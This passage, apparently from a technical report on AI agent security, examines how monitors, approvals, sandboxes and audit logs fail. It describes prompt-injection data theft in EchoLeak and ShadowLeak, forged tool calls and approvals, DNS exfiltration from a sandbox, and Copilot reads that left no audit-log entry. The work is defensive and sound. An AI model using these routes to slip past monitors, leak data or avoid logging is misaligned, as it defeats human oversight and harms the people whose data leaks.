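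The `export_pdf` tool uploads a new file and destroys nothing, so its author could correctly mark it non-destructive, and even this rule would then miss it. Codex CLI would still prompt the user. For a non-destructive tool that writes, it skips the prompt only if the tool also declares that it does not reach external systems.

### Restrictions in public repositories

Developers can also restrict an agent's tools in a project's configuration files. *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (Madatha, 2026) analysed 10,008 public GitHub repositories containing 6,145 configuration files for coding agents. Only 31 of those files (0.5%) declared explicit permissions, compared with 33% of the 24,436 workflow files for GitHub Actions, a service that runs automated jobs such as software tests.

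Madatha calls the result indicative, because agent configurations have no standard syntax for permissions. The search produced 37 matches, six of them false positives, and it may have missed others. Many of the files are also plain-language instructions, which are unlikely to contain a formal permission list.

An agent without a declaration may still be restricted, since the application may ask before running commands or an administrator may have set limits elsewhere. Madatha notes that several coding tools do little or nothing to enforce permissions written in an agent's definition, so a declaration does not guarantee a restriction.

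Copying configuration files could spread an omission from one project to another. Madatha reports that 10.1% of the configuration files in the study are exact copies of files in other repositories, after adjusting for copied projects. About four-fifths of the files studied are GitHub Actions workflows and the rest are agent files, so this percentage does not show how often developers copy agent configurations.

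### Missing checks among reported vulnerabilities

Estimates of the share of reported flaws caused by missing or incomplete checks depend heavily on what researchers count. *It's Not Just XSS Anymore*, a blog post by the security vendor Safety, classifies roughly a third of bugs in AI frameworks as broken access control or missing authentication. *aiAuthZ* (2026) attributes seven of 11 documented agent failures to problems with identity or authorisation. Its broad definition includes cases where a document or message the agent trusted caused an action no authorised person had requested, which would cover many prompt injections. Even if the 11 cases were a random sample, they would be compatible with a true share anywhere from about 31% to 89%.

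*LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (2026) classifies 295 GitHub security advisories by standard categories of software weakness. Injection flaws were the largest group, and the overall pattern resembled that of conventional software.

None of these categories corresponds closely to a failure of complete mediation. A missing login on an administration page is a missing check, but it may have nothing to do with tool calls. A code injection flaw is in a different category but can still defeat mediation, because the attacker's code may run without the agent making a tool call that a monitor could refuse. The published shares therefore do not measure how often side-effecting tools bypass a monitor.

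Report counts are also a poor measure of the number of separate faults. *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* (2026) traces 13 advisories to a single cause, permission checks that relied on identity fields that could change, such as display names. Safety found that one agent framework accounted for 120 advisories from a concentrated group of disclosures. *The Agent Incident Registry* (2026) assigns 964 category codes to 451 records, so its categories overlap, and it warns against reading them as an estimate of real-world risk.

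### How private deployments compare

Most of this evidence comes from public code, and private systems may be better or worse protected. When Yao and colleagues added seven closed-source applications, including Claude Code and Cursor, to their comparison, the share of pairs with no enforced approval fell from 60.7% to 47.5%. Since every application had equal weight, the size of the drop implies that almost none of the pairs involving those seven lacked approval. But for these applications they relied on documentation, not source code, and companies that use the products may change the default settings.

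Proprietary agent systems can be poorly protected. Eykholt, Kirat and colleagues (2026) tested two such systems in 2025 and describe the results in *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems*. They could run arbitrary code on each system's hosting platform, and that code could open outbound network connections. One system checked commands against a list of permitted programs but missed ways those programs could start others. The other had a debugging interface that ran custom tools without involving the model.

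Two systems are too few to estimate how common such weaknesses are in private deployments. Public surveys cannot cover a tool that a company wrote for itself. If `export_pdf` is an in-house tool, Ana's company will have to compare the tool's description with its code or observe what the tool sends over the network.

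## Failures reported in released products

The vendor's advisory or the finder's account of a fault in a released agent product often identifies the exact check that was missing, which surveys of public code rarely do. Nearly all the reports come from researchers who demonstrated a fault and told the vendor. They show what an attacker could have done with a product that customers were already using, but few establish whether anyone did it.

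### Tool calls that no model requested

In an ordinary agent loop, software runs a tool when the model outputs a tool call. In August 2026, Hedi Ingber and Aviyam Ivgi, co-founders of the company Stealth, told the Black Hat security conference that agent software from Amazon Web Services (AWS), Google and Vercel did not always check that a tool call came from the model. They call the pattern CoreBreak. According to The Hacker News' *AWS, Google, and Vercel Agent Flaws Let Attackers Trigger Tools* (2026), the software accepted data structured like a tool call as if the model had produced it. In several of the affected paths the model never ran, so instructions in its prompt and filters on its output had no effect.

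The AWS fault was in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, a service that runs agents on AWS's servers. A customer's application sends the conversation to AgentCore, which runs the loop. According to AWS's *CVE-2026-18830* (2026), the loop could run a tool call taken directly from the caller's message, skipping the model and the security controls that depend on it. The caller had to be authenticated and could reach only the tools the customer had configured. If Ana's company had used the service, a colleague with permission to ask for invoice summaries might have been able to run `send_email` with any recipient and text.

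AWS now rejects tool calls that a caller supplies. It made the change on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. AWS lists the service as affected before 31 July 2026 but does not say when the fault began.

A similar path remains in Strands, the open-source library on which, according to Ingber and Ivgi, AWS built the AgentCore loop. A comment in the code describes the shortcut, which is deliberate. In April, a contributor proposed removing it and warned that outsiders might be able to insert tool calls, but the project closed the proposal in June without adopting it. The Hacker News found the shortcut still in place on 5 August. AWS treated the behaviour as a vulnerability in its hosted service but as a documented feature of the library. It tells developers to build the message history from their own application, not from anything a caller can influence. The researchers say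 AWS told them this was the customer's responsibility.

Google's fault was in its Agent Development Kit (ADK), which lets a developer require a person's confirmation before a sensitive tool runs. *CVE-2026-18236 Detail* (2026), an entry in the United States' National Vulnerability Database (NVD), reports that ADK did not verify that the tool belonged to the agent, that it needed confirmation, or that the confirmed arguments matched the original call. Anyone able to insert events into a session's history could forge an approval. To exclude this kind of failure, SecureClaw's first theorem assumes that Ana's click on one e-mail cannot release another. Google added the three checks in version 2.5.0, released on 16 July. That version also stopped an optional mode for resuming interrupted sessions from accepting tool calls written by the user.

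Vercel's fault was in two packages that connect coding agents to tools outside their sandbox. As NVD's *CVE-2026-64650 Detail* describes, the component that passed on tool requests accepted them from any process whose command line contained the path of an approved helper program, which does not prove that the model made the request. Hostile code already running in the sandbox, for example from a compromised dependency, could use the outside tools to look up secrets or deploy software. The fixed versions, published on 10 July, require each request to have a short-lived, single-use authorisation that matches the tool and input the model requested.

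Vercel's remedy resembles SecureClaw's approval step, but Vercel's authorisation shows only that the model made the request, not that a policy allowed it, as a SecureClaw approval does. A model that has read the planted sentence in the supplier's note can make a harmful request, and Vercel's new check would let it through. The CoreBreak fixes restore the link between the model and its tools, but they do not replace a policy check at the tool, which would have applied the same rules to forged and genuine calls.

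### EchoLeak and the chat window

Data can also leave without an explicit tool call, through the window that displays the model's answer. Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their e-mail and files. In January 2025, researchers at the security company Aim Security found a fault, later known as EchoLeak, that an outsider could exploit by sending an employee an e-mail. If the employee then asked Copilot a question that led it to retrieve the message, Copilot could disclose internal data without the employee clicking on anything.

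Microsoft had several defences against this, and *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) describes how each failed. A classifier that looked for planted instructions in incoming text missed an e-mail that read like ordinary business correspondence. A filter that removed outside links from Copilot's answers did not recognise every way of writing a link. A browser rule allowed the chat window to load content only from approved addresses, but one of these belonged to a Microsoft service that would fetch content from other addresses on request, so the rule in effect allowed any address that service could reach.

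As a result, the chat window could send internal data to an outsider by loading an image. This was a failure of complete mediation, although few people would count a chat window among an agent's tools. A monitor on Ana's four tools would have detected no e-mail, PDF export or shell command. The image request came after the model had finished its answer, much as the upload in `export_pdf` came after the monitor had approved the call.

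Labels could have helped. Copilot's answer combined an outsider's message with internal documents, so FIDES's rule would have labelled it untrusted and restricted it to people allowed to read those documents. A policy could then have refused to load outside images for the answer, but only if the designers had recognised that displaying an answer was a sink.

Reddy and Gujral recommend marking outside text with tags and instructing the model not to follow commands inside them, but this still depends on the model following that instruction. They also propose stricter browser rules and access control based on where data came from, neither of which depends on the model following instructions.

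Microsoft began staged repairs in April 2025, completed the fix on its servers in May and published its advisory on 11 June. The attack path was therefore open for about four months after its discovery, and for an unknown time before. Microsoft reported no known attacks on customers. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case of a prompt injection weaponised to take data from a production system, but they describe a demonstration by researchers.

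A related fault affected ChatGPT's Deep Research, an agent that browses the web and can read a user's Gmail. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes how hidden text in an e-mail could make the agent include private data in the address of a page it visited. Visiting the page sent the data out, as the read-only searches did in Mohammadi and colleagues' experiments. The request came from the service's own servers, so a filter on the user's browser or company network could not have stopped it. Researchers reported the problem, called ShadowLeak, in June 2025, and it was fixed in early August.

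### Approved commands and published output

Coding agents increasingly work without anyone watching each step. On a public software project, an agent may read a change proposed by a stranger, run commands to investigate it and post the output in the discussion of that change. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* (2026) reports that Elad Meged of Novee Security tested agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI in this setup.

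Anthropic's automated workflow disclosed secrets because it approved commands that looked safe and published their output by default. Each decision was defensible alone, but the approval covered only running the command, and the harm came from publishing its output. A confidentiality label on the output would have connected the two decisions. Under the policy of Costa and colleagues, a monitor would have refused to post output that depended on a secret, because anyone can read a public discussion.

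Anthropic patched each finding and paid a bounty for it, but Meged kept finding ways around the patches. Each patch closed the specific hole he had reported, and the next attack used another place where the same kind of decision was made.

Meged used Google's Gemini CLI in the configuration that Google recommends for automated workflows handling untrusted input, and a restriction that the operator had set did not apply when the agent acted. Google's advisory has a severity score of 10.0, the maximum. For Ana's company, this would be like forbidding `run_shell` in a rule that the component running the commands never checks.

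OpenAI's Codex CLI, by contrast, had a problem with integrity labels. When stages of a workflow shared a workspace, later stages treated the output of earlier ones as trusted. A stranger's text could therefore lose its untrusted status when the agent saved it, as in Cai and colleagues' memory case. Google's advisory supports Meged's account of its product, and Anthropic's bounties support his account of its workflow. It is not known how long any of these faults had existed.

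### A sandbox that still looked up addresses

AgentCore also includes a Code Interpreter, which runs code that an agent writes. AWS described the interpreter's Sandbox mode as "complete isolation with no external access". A customer could reasonably let the agent run any Python analysis there, assuming the code could not send data out.

BeyondTrust (2026) found that the sandbox blocked ordinary connections but allowed DNS queries, the lookups that translate a domain name into a network address. Whoever controls a domain also controls the servers that answer queries for it, so the name being looked up can carry data to them. In the researchers' first test, the connection seemed to fail, but the lookup reached a server they controlled. A customer who tested the isolation by trying to open a web page would have wrongly concluded that it worked.

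The lookup took place below the level of any tool call, so a monitor could have checked and approved every request to run code without having any control over the lookup.

The interpreter's permissions determined how much data could leak. A default role in AWS's starter toolkit could read everything the account stored in S3 (AWS's storage service) and all the passwords and keys in its secrets manager. BeyondTrust considered this far more access than a code interpreter should have. With a narrower role, the outbound path would still have been open, but hostile code would have had much less data to send through it.

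The repair took more than seven months.

| Date | What happened |
|---|---|
| 1 September 2025 | BeyondTrust reports the fault |
| 4 September 2025 | AWS reproduces it |
| 1 November 2025 | AWS deploys a first fix |
| 17 November 2025 | AWS tells the researchers that it has withdrawn the fix |
| 23 December 2025 | AWS decides to change the documentation instead |
| 16 March 2026 | BeyondTrust publishes its findings |
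| 15 April 2026 | AWS closes the path |

AWS said in a statement that the service was operating as expected. It said sandbox mode needed DNS lookups to reach S3, and customers who wanted complete isolation could use another mode, in which they configure a private network themselves. AWS now describes sandbox mode in its documentation as providing "limited external network access" to AWS services. This wording is more accurate and lets careful customers plan for the exception. But the change did not protect customers who had relied on the original wording, because the code could still send data out just as before.

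The permitted route to S3 may also be a problem, since Sonrai Security's *Global S3* reports that sandboxed code can use it as another channel for communicating with an attacker. S3 stores data for AWS customers generally, so permission to reach it isn't limited to one company's files. The approved address in EchoLeak had the same weakness, because both rules allowed requests to a service when the outcome depended on what the service would do with them.

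### Which condition failed and who noticed

The table compares the cases whose accounts give at least some dates. The durations are minimums because no vendor or researcher established when any of the faults first appeared.

| Case | Promised boundary | What the check missed | Known exposure |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentCore tool calls | The model and its controls come before every tool call | Whether the call came from the model | Until 31 July 2026 |
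| Google ADK | A person confirms sensitive calls | Whether the approval matched the call | Until version 2.5.0, 16 July 2026 |
| Vercel packages | Outside tools run only when the model requests them | Whether the model had made the request | Until fixed versions on 10 July 2026 |
| EchoLeak | Answers cannot send data to unapproved addresses | Where an approved service would forward a request | January to May 2025 |
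| AgentCore sandbox | Code has no external access | DNS lookups | September 2025 to April 2026, apart from a short-lived fix |

Google's and Vercel's customers stopped being exposed on those dates only if they upgraded at once. AWS and Microsoft could repair their hosted services for everyone, but a company that installs a package keeps the fault until it installs a new version. Errors in public records can make the need to upgrade harder to notice. NVD's description of the fault in Vercel's Codex package names the OpenCode package, so a company searching for Codex could overlook the warning.

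All five cases in the table are mainly failures of mediation, though the CoreBreak faults also involve a kind of mislabelling. The software treated a caller's message, a forged approval or a sandboxed process as trustworthy because it inferred the source from something easy to inspect, such as the structure of a message or the path in a command line. An integrity label attached when the data arrived would have recorded its actual source.

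The failure in Anthropic's workflow partly involved confidentiality labels, because command output had no label to stop its publication. None of the cases was caused by a missed field like the account number under "remit to", but this is weak evidence that missed fields are rare in products. A researcher can prove that a check is missing by making a forbidden action succeed, but proving that a field has the wrong label requires knowing what the customer meant to protect, and outsiders usually don't know that.

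Outside researchers found all of these faults, and none of the accounts describes a vendor's or customer's monitoring system detecting a fault first. In June 2026, Vercel fixed a related weakness that let a client forge tool approvals, and credited Anthropic's security team and Claude, Anthropic's AI model, with finding it. Many of the underlying mistakes are old, and Eykholt and colleagues argue that agent vulnerabilities often repeat classes of weakness long known in other software.

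### Why the reports do not give a failure rate

A failure rate needs a count of failures and a count of the systems or actions in which a failure could have occurred. Disclosures supply an incomplete version of the first and nothing for the second. Suppose there are N agent products, a share f of them have a serious fault, researchers examine a share e, they find a share d of the faults in those products, and a share p of the findings become public. If researchers choose products without regard to their faults, the expected number of faulty products with a public report is

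D = N × f × e × d × p.

Five reports among 1,000 products could mean that 0.5% are faulty, if researchers examined every product and found and published every fault. They could also mean that every product is faulty, if researchers examined 20, found half the faults and published half of what they found. For agents, nobody has good estimates of the share of products examined, the share of faults found or the share of findings published.

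Researchers also don't choose products at random. AgentCore had both the tool-call fault and the DNS fault. SC Media's *Amazon Bedrock agent vulnerability allowed credential theft and code access* describes a third problem, in which Zenity Labs obtained an agent's temporary credentials and used its excessive permissions to reach other agents. AWS addressed parts of that problem in February and September 2026. *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Flaws Could Expose AWS Credentials* (Mascellino, 2026), also from September, reports two vulnerabilities in AgentCore's development kit. These reports may mean that AgentCore is unusually weak, or that a prominent service attracts researchers, who then build on one another's work. A product with no reports may be safer, or it may not have been examined.

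Whether a flaw is made public also depends on the vendor. TNW's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties* reports that the three companies paid researchers for agent flaws and then kept quiet about them. Vendors can more easily stay quiet about flaws in hosted services because customers have nothing to install. Microsoft did publish an advisory for EchoLeak, and its *CVE-2026-26129 M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* records another Copilot flaw that required no action from customers. If a vendor fixed a similar flaw without publishing an advisory, a survey would not count it.

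Even the published cases have no natural unit for counting. CoreBreak is a single presentation that covers six ways to reach a tool: the AgentCore service, the Strands library, two paths in Google's kit and Vercel's two packages. Only four have a CVE number, the standard identifier for a public vulnerability. AWS issued none for Strands, and Google's second path has none, though it shares a release with the first. BeyondTrust's timeline for the DNS fault gives severity scores but no CVE number, so a count based on CVE numbers could omit a fault that stayed open for most of seven months.

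Vendors classify these faults inconsistently too, so failures of mediation are as hard to count here as in the wider surveys of advisories. Google and Vercel classified their CoreBreak faults as incorrect authorisation, while AWS classified its own as improper input validation. Microsoft classified EchoLeak as injection, according to GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711*. Microsoft scored EchoLeak's severity at 9.3 and the National Vulnerability Database scored it at 7.5, so severity scores cannot establish which cases matter most either.

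The rate of actual harm is even harder to estimate. Microsoft said it knew of no attacks using EchoLeak, but the advisories and CVE records for CoreBreak contain no information on whether anyone used those faults against a live system before the fixes. The number of such attacks is therefore unknown and can't be counted as zero.

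## Why the failures go unnoticed

Outside researchers found the faults in released products by looking for them. A company that relies on its own users, logs or test results may never find such a fault, because missed fields and unchecked tools rarely affect the work that people see.

When the gateway misses a protected field, the agent's job can become easier. The runtime receives the account number in readable form and every tool accepts it, so nothing raises an error. Task completion rates don't reveal the missed fields either, since they stayed above 80% in Ma and Schmid's tests even when the gateway missed a fifth of the protected fields.

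People notice excessive restriction much sooner than leaks. In *AgentLeak*, El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah (2026) tested 50 scenarios with agents barred from sharing any sensitive data with one another, and only 35% to 65% of tasks succeeded. Users complain about failures like these, whereas a supplier whose account number has leaked usually doesn't know. A team that changes its rules mainly in response to complaints will therefore tend to loosen them. SecureClaw is a partial exception because over-marking hardly affected its task completion, so users might not report that error either.

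### Forbidden actions that return success

A tool can report success even when the policy forbids the action, because the report only confirms that the tool ran. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) measured how often this hides a failure in the airline tasks of τ²-bench, a benchmark in which an agent handles customer requests by editing a database of bookings. The model has to follow the airline's rules from a written document, and the tools don't enforce them. For example, the cancellation tool checks that a booking exists and then cancels it, even if the fare rules forbid that.

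With GPT-4o mini as the agent, 78% of the failures left the database in the wrong state without any tool reporting an error. The agent succeeded in only 29.6% of 250 runs, so if the 78% holds for those runs, more than half of them ended with a wrong database and no error message. The agent's own report did not reveal the failures either. In one task, the customer gives false information to obtain a cancellation that the rules forbid, and an agent that is misled reports a successful cancellation. Agents without extra checks handled this task correctly in at most one of 16 runs.

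The 78% can include omitted changes as well as forbidden actions, because either can leave the database wrong. To see how much forbidden actions contributed, Reddy and colleagues added four gates, which are short programs that check a proposed change against the database and the rules before the tool runs. Success rose to 42.0%, and a repeat with 750 new runs gave almost the same improvement. One gate, which blocks ineligible cancellations, accounted for nearly all of the improvement. An audit found that all 161 of its refusals were correct, but only two of the 42 refusals by the baggage gate were.

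The benchmark's retail tools enforce many of their own rules and return an error when a call breaks one. Gates did not help on the retail tasks, where 40 of 64 runs succeeded without gates and 37 of 64 with them, a difference within the margin of error. This supports the explanation that failures go unnoticed because tools accept forbidden calls, although the comparison covers only eight retail tasks.

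The problem persisted with a stronger model. GPT-5.2 triggered the gates in 43 of 250 airline runs, and its success rate rose from 61.2% to 71.6% with them, though Reddy and colleagues have not replicated that result. *How Strongly Should Task State Influence an LLM Agent?* (2026) reports a separate test of Qwen3-235B on the airline tasks. In 54 of 100 runs without a gate, the agent made at least one change that was not in the reference solution. In 35 of these it only made extra changes, in nine it used the right tools with the wrong details, and in ten it did both. All the extra changes went through, though some may have broken no rule.

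The gates can also fail silently. If one crashes, the test software records the error and lets the call proceed. Reddy and colleagues chose this behaviour so that a bug in a gate would not block legitimate work, but a crashed gate then has the same effect on the booking as an approval, and somebody has to read the error record to tell them apart.

Ana's `export_pdf` would look equally normal, because Ben receives a link that works.

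Analyses of past incidents cover only the silent failures that somebody eventually discovered. *Discriminating Fixture Coverage in Agent-Infrastructure Verification Suites* (Xu and Tao, 2026) cites a taxonomy of silent failures in one production agent runtime, which Wu (2026) based on the operators' postmortems. Such a taxonomy can show how failures stay hidden for a while, but not how many remain hidden.

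### Gaps in the log

A monitor can log only the calls that reach it. If Ana's company reads its monitor's log after the account number appears on the public web, it will find an approved e-mail to Ben but no record of the upload, because calls to `export_pdf` bypass the monitor. Every entry is accurate, but an investigator who treats the log as a full history of the agent's actions will conclude that the agent sent only the e-mail.

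A product's own audit log can also omit events it is supposed to record. In July 2025, Zack Korman, the chief technology officer of the security company Pistachio, found such a gap in Microsoft 365 Copilot. According to Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You*, Copilot normally left an entry in the customer's audit log when it summarised a file, but if the user asked it to leave out the link to the file, it produced the summary without leaving an entry. This suggests that the entry depended on the link appearing in the answer rather than on Copilot reading the file.

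An employee about to join a competitor could have used Copilot to read files without leaving a record in the audit log. Entries could also go missing by accident. Korman was testing software that relied on the log, so he knew which files Copilot had just read, and he noticed that some entries were missing.

Microsoft rated the flaw "important" and told Korman that a full fix would arrive on 17 August. It assigned no CVE number because customers had nothing to install, and it told him it did not plan to notify them. Michael Bargury of the security company Zenity had disclosed the same problem a year earlier.

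Most of this account rests on Korman's word. Petri's *Microsoft Fixes Critical Copilot Flaw Allowing Audit Log Evasion* attributes its description to his post, and the summary in the OECD's *Microsoft Copilot Flaw Enables Undetectable Access to Sensitive Files* (2025) is AI-generated, so neither adds much independent confirmation. Pistachio also sells security products. But Korman published the requests alongside the resulting logs, and any customer could easily have tested the behaviour he describes before the fix. He reports missing records but no failure of file permissions. It is probably impossible to establish how many reads went unrecorded, because customers would look for them in the audit log.

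Better protection for logs would solve only part of this. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) reviews 71 works on recording and tracing what agents do, and finds that few report logs that reveal tampering or carry proof of their origin. The review is a curated selection, so other systems may have these features. Without them, a compromised runtime that keeps its own log could delete or alter entries unnoticed. But tamper protection only covers entries that were written, so it would not have helped with the ones Copilot never wrote.

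### Leaks outside the final answer

Many privacy tests check only the agent's final answer. El Yagoubi and colleagues built the AgentLeak benchmark to find out what such tests miss when several agents share a task. Each of its 1,000 scenarios typically has 29 private fields, and the task needs about three of them. The benchmark counts a leak when any other private field appears in one of seven channels.

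| Channel | Example in Ana's company | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|---|
| Final output | The agent's answer to Ana | 27.2% |
| Messages between agents | A request to a second agent that checks invoices | 68.8% |
| Shared memory | Notes that several agents can read | 46.7% |
| Tool inputs | The text passed to `send_email` | 62% to 86%, depending on the model |
| Logs | Debugging records | Higher than for tool inputs |
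| Tool outputs | The data `read_invoice` returns | No large-scale figure |
| Stored files | A PDF the agent creates | No large-scale figure |

The first three rates come from 4,979 runs in which a coordinating agent delegated work to a second agent. The runs used five models from OpenAI, Anthropic, Meta and Mistral. The results for tool inputs and logs come from a smaller test with 100 scenarios per model.

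In 2,076 of the 4,979 runs, the final answer was clean but a message or shared memory contained a leak. About 3,430 runs leaked in at least one of the three main channels, so an audit of final answers would have missed 61% of the runs with a leak. El Yagoubi and colleagues understate this result when they write that such audits miss 41.7% of violations, because 41.7% is the share of all runs, including those without a leak.

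Such an audit would also have made the riskier design look safer. When a single agent worked alone, its final answer leaked in 43.2% of runs. Adding a second agent reduced that figure to 27.2% but raised the share of runs with a leak anywhere to 68.9%. In a separate set of scenarios without attacks, an output filter also cut leaks in final answers, from 48% to 1%, while the rate in internal channels stayed at 31%. A company that installed the filter and then audited only the answers would find almost no leaks.

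An attack detector would not have helped much. Messages leaked in 69.3% of runs without an attack and in 66.3% of runs with the strongest attacks. The agents passed on whole records as part of ordinary delegation, so in most cases there was no suspicious instruction to detect.

A language model found most of the leaks, so the rates depend on its accuracy. On labelled excerpts, the full detection system caught 93.4% of leaks and wrongly flagged 4.8% of clean excerpts. El Yagoubi and colleagues call their rates lower bounds because the system misses some leaks, but this ignores the false alarms. If the same error rates applied to whole runs, a true leak rate t would produce an observed rate of

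0.934t + 0.048(1 − t).

Solving for t gives about 72% for messages and 25% for final answers. The correction slightly lowers the figure for final answers, but the large gap between the channels remains.

Many of these leaks may do no harm. The benchmark counts unnecessary sharing as a leak even when the same company runs both agents, and El Yagoubi and colleagues do not claim that every case is a breach. The sharing becomes dangerous if an attacker controls the second agent or can read the stored messages.

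Ma and Schmid found an even wider gap when they ran the benchmark's 496 attacked scenarios without a defence. The final answer leaked information in 33.47% of them, and messages between agents leaked information in 92.74%. In total, 466 scenarios had a leak in the answer, the messages or shared memory, and in 300 of those the final answer contained no leak.

The comparison of defences shows that auditing only the final answers can make a defence that reduces leaks overall appear to make privacy worse. IPIGuard and DRIFT try to stop planted instructions from changing an agent's plan. IPIGuard reduced the share of scenarios with any leak from 94% to 79%, and DRIFT reduced it to 72%. Over the same scenarios, the share with a leak in the final answer rose from 33% to 56% with IPIGuard and 51% with DRIFT.

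### What zero successful attacks can show

SecureClaw's result on Agent Security Bench, with no successes in 2,000 attacks, sounds close to a proof of safety. Its statistical meaning is narrower. If each attack succeeded independently with probability p, the chance of seeing no successes would be (1 − p)²⁰⁰⁰. A two-sided 95% confidence interval extends to the value of p at which that chance falls to 2.5%:

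(1 − p)²⁰⁰⁰ = 0.025, so p = 1 − 0.025^(1/2000) ≈ 0.0018.

The result therefore rules out, at the usual level of confidence, a success rate above about 0.18% for attacks drawn from the same distribution.

The trials may not be fully independent. The 2,000 attacks use five styles of planted instruction, with 400 cases each. If the five styles reuse the same 400 cases, and a case that resists one style tends to resist the others, the test could provide as little information as 400 independent trials, and the upper limit would be 0.92%. Counting the runs on four other models as extra trials would be misleading, because those runs used the same attacks and the same executor.

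A larger sample would not make the result apply to a tool outside the test. Suppose that a share u of real attacks uses a tool that skips the executor, and that these attacks succeed at rate s. The overall success rate is then

r = (1 − u)p + us.

The executor was in place throughout the benchmark, so u was zero and the 2,000 trials contain no information about s. If 1% of attacks on Ana's company used `export_pdf` and half of those succeeded, those attacks alone would add 0.5 percentage points to the overall success rate, well above the 0.18% limit. If every attack used the tool, the rate would be 50%.

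Field labels raise the same problem. When a benchmark's designers specify which fields are protected and give the defence those labels, the test cannot include a field like "remit to" that everyone overlooked. A low attack success rate is good evidence of how the defence handles known tools and fields, but it does not show whether the company's lists of tools and fields are complete.

Few benchmarks could reveal the silent rule-breaking seen in the airline tasks. Reddy and colleagues argue that to do so, a benchmark needs structured tool calls, tools that accept forbidden actions, rules that a program can check against the database, scoring based on the final state, and tasks that lead agents to break the rules. They looked for a second benchmark with all these features and found none. The closest was WorkBench, a set of office tasks, but its tasks rarely led agents to break a rule. On BFCL,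 a function-calling test, their check never fired in 200 tasks. Wang and colleagues found that no benchmark in their catalogue evaluates the whole chain of evidence and actions behind an agent's output.

Xu and Tao point out that, from the outside, a system whose checks never report a failure looks the same as a system that never fails. Ana's company could run its monitor for a year without an alert and still not know whether the monitor was missing failures or there were none to report, unless someone deliberately introduced a fault.

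### Records from outside the agent

A company has other sources of evidence, each of which can expose some of the failures described here. It can watch its network traffic, plant invented values and search for them, or compare the monitor's log with the records of the services that the agent uses.

| Failure | Network monitoring | Planted values | Comparison with service records |
|---|---|---|---|
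| A missed account number passes between agents on one machine | No | Yes, if someone searches the messages | No |
| An approved e-mail contains a missed account number | Only if it can read the message | Yes, if someone searches sent mail | No, because the e-mail has a matching approval |
| `export_pdf` uploads an invoice | Yes, if the traffic crosses the company's network | Yes, if someone opens the uploaded file | Yes, if the company can obtain the hosting service's records |
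| An agent cancels a booking against the rules | No | No | No, because both records show the same cancellation |

Network monitoring is most useful against tools that bypass the monitor. It would also have to cover address lookups, which carried data out of Amazon's sandbox. It cannot detect requests that a hosted agent sends from its provider's own servers, as in ShadowLeak. A connection to an approved service can also look normal even if that service forwards the data elsewhere, as in EchoLeak.

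Planted values produce almost no false alarms, but they miss any leak that changes the wording. In AgentLeak, exact markers accounted for 8% of the classified leaks, recognisable formats such as card numbers for 10%, and paraphrases for 82%. These shares appear to come from 226 leaks, far fewer than the benchmark found in total. Markers should work better for account numbers, which are of little use unless copied exactly. El Yagoubi and colleagues suspect that models have learned to suppress obvious markers, so Ana's company would do better to plant a realistic invented number in a test invoice than a string labelled as a secret.

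Someone also has to collect the messages and logs before searching them, which creates another copy of the data. In the smaller AgentLeak test, Claude 3.5 Sonnet leaked private fields into its logs in 85% of scenarios, compared with 74% for tool inputs. A company that keeps fuller logs to catch leaks has to protect those logs as carefully as the original invoices.

Comparing records works when an outside service keeps its own record of what happened. Ana's company could match every message in its mail provider's records to an approval in the monitor's log, and any message without an approval would reveal a route around the monitor. Korman made his discovery in a similar way, by comparing reads he knew about with the entries in the audit log. The method fails for services that the company doesn't know its agent is using, because the company has no reason to ask them for records.

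None of the three methods catches the wrongly cancelled booking, because the agent used a registered tool, the request went to the usual database, and the records all show the same events. To find the error, someone has to compare the booking with the fare rules, as the cancellation gate did before the change took effect.

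## Testing labels and mediation by planting faults

A company can find out whether its tests would detect a broken control by breaking the control on purpose. Suppose Ana's company passes all its security tests, then removes the monitor's check on `export_pdf` and runs the tests again. If they still pass, the first result was no evidence that the check worked. Attack benchmarks often have this weakness because they exercise only the tools and fields their designers listed.

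Testing a system by planting faults in it is called mutation testing, which software engineers developed in the 1970s for ordinary programs. A mutant is a copy of the system with one deliberate fault. A test kills a mutant if it gives a different result on the mutant than on the original, and the mutation score is the share of mutants that the tests kill.

### Faults in access rules

*A Fault Model and Mutation Testing of Access Control Policies* (Martin and Xie, 2007) applied the method to rules about who may use what. Each test is a request, and the result is a decision to permit or deny it. In one example, the first rule stops three named users from distributing a document, and the second permits everyone else. Reversing the first rule's effect produces a mutant that permits everyone. Only a request from one of the three users kills this mutant, because the original denies that request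 and both versions permit requests from anyone else.

The same example shows why coverage, the share of rules and conditions that the tests reach, can mislead. Two requests, one from the first named user and one from a user who isn't named, reach both rules and both outcomes of the condition, which gives 100% coverage on all three measures Martin and Xie define. But if someone mistypes the second user's name in the rule, that user can distribute the document, and neither request reveals the error. Tests of a labelling rule that recognises several names for an account number have the same weakness if the test invoices use only one of those names.

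Some mutants behave exactly like the original policy, for example when an earlier rule always overrides the one that changed. No test can kill these mutants, so counting them makes the tests look worse than they are. Martin and Xie removed some of them using a tool that compares two policies.

Mutation testing takes the current policy as its standard, so it evaluates the tests, not whether the policy is correct. If the labelling rule already omits "remit to", the original version and nearly every mutant will give the runtime the account number, so comparing them is unlikely to reveal the omission. Someone still has to decide independently which fields need protection.

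### Runs that differ only in a secret

A tester can check noninterference by running the system twice with different secrets and confirming that everything an outsider can see is the same. This doesn't require knowing the correct output for every input. In *Testing Noninterference, Quickly* (2014), Hriţcu, Lampropoulos and colleagues automated this test for small simulated computers that label each value as secret or public. They used the testing tool QuickCheck to generate random programs and search for a pair of runs that violates noninterference.

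QuickCheck quickly found a flaw in their first design, using a program that writes a public 1 into one of two public memory locations, depending on a secret value. Anyone who reads the memory afterwards can learn the secret from the location of the 1. The researchers then made the written value secret too, but QuickCheck found that the changed label itself revealed the location, since an observer in their model can see labels. The design that worked prevents a program from overwriting a public location if the choice of location depends on a secret.

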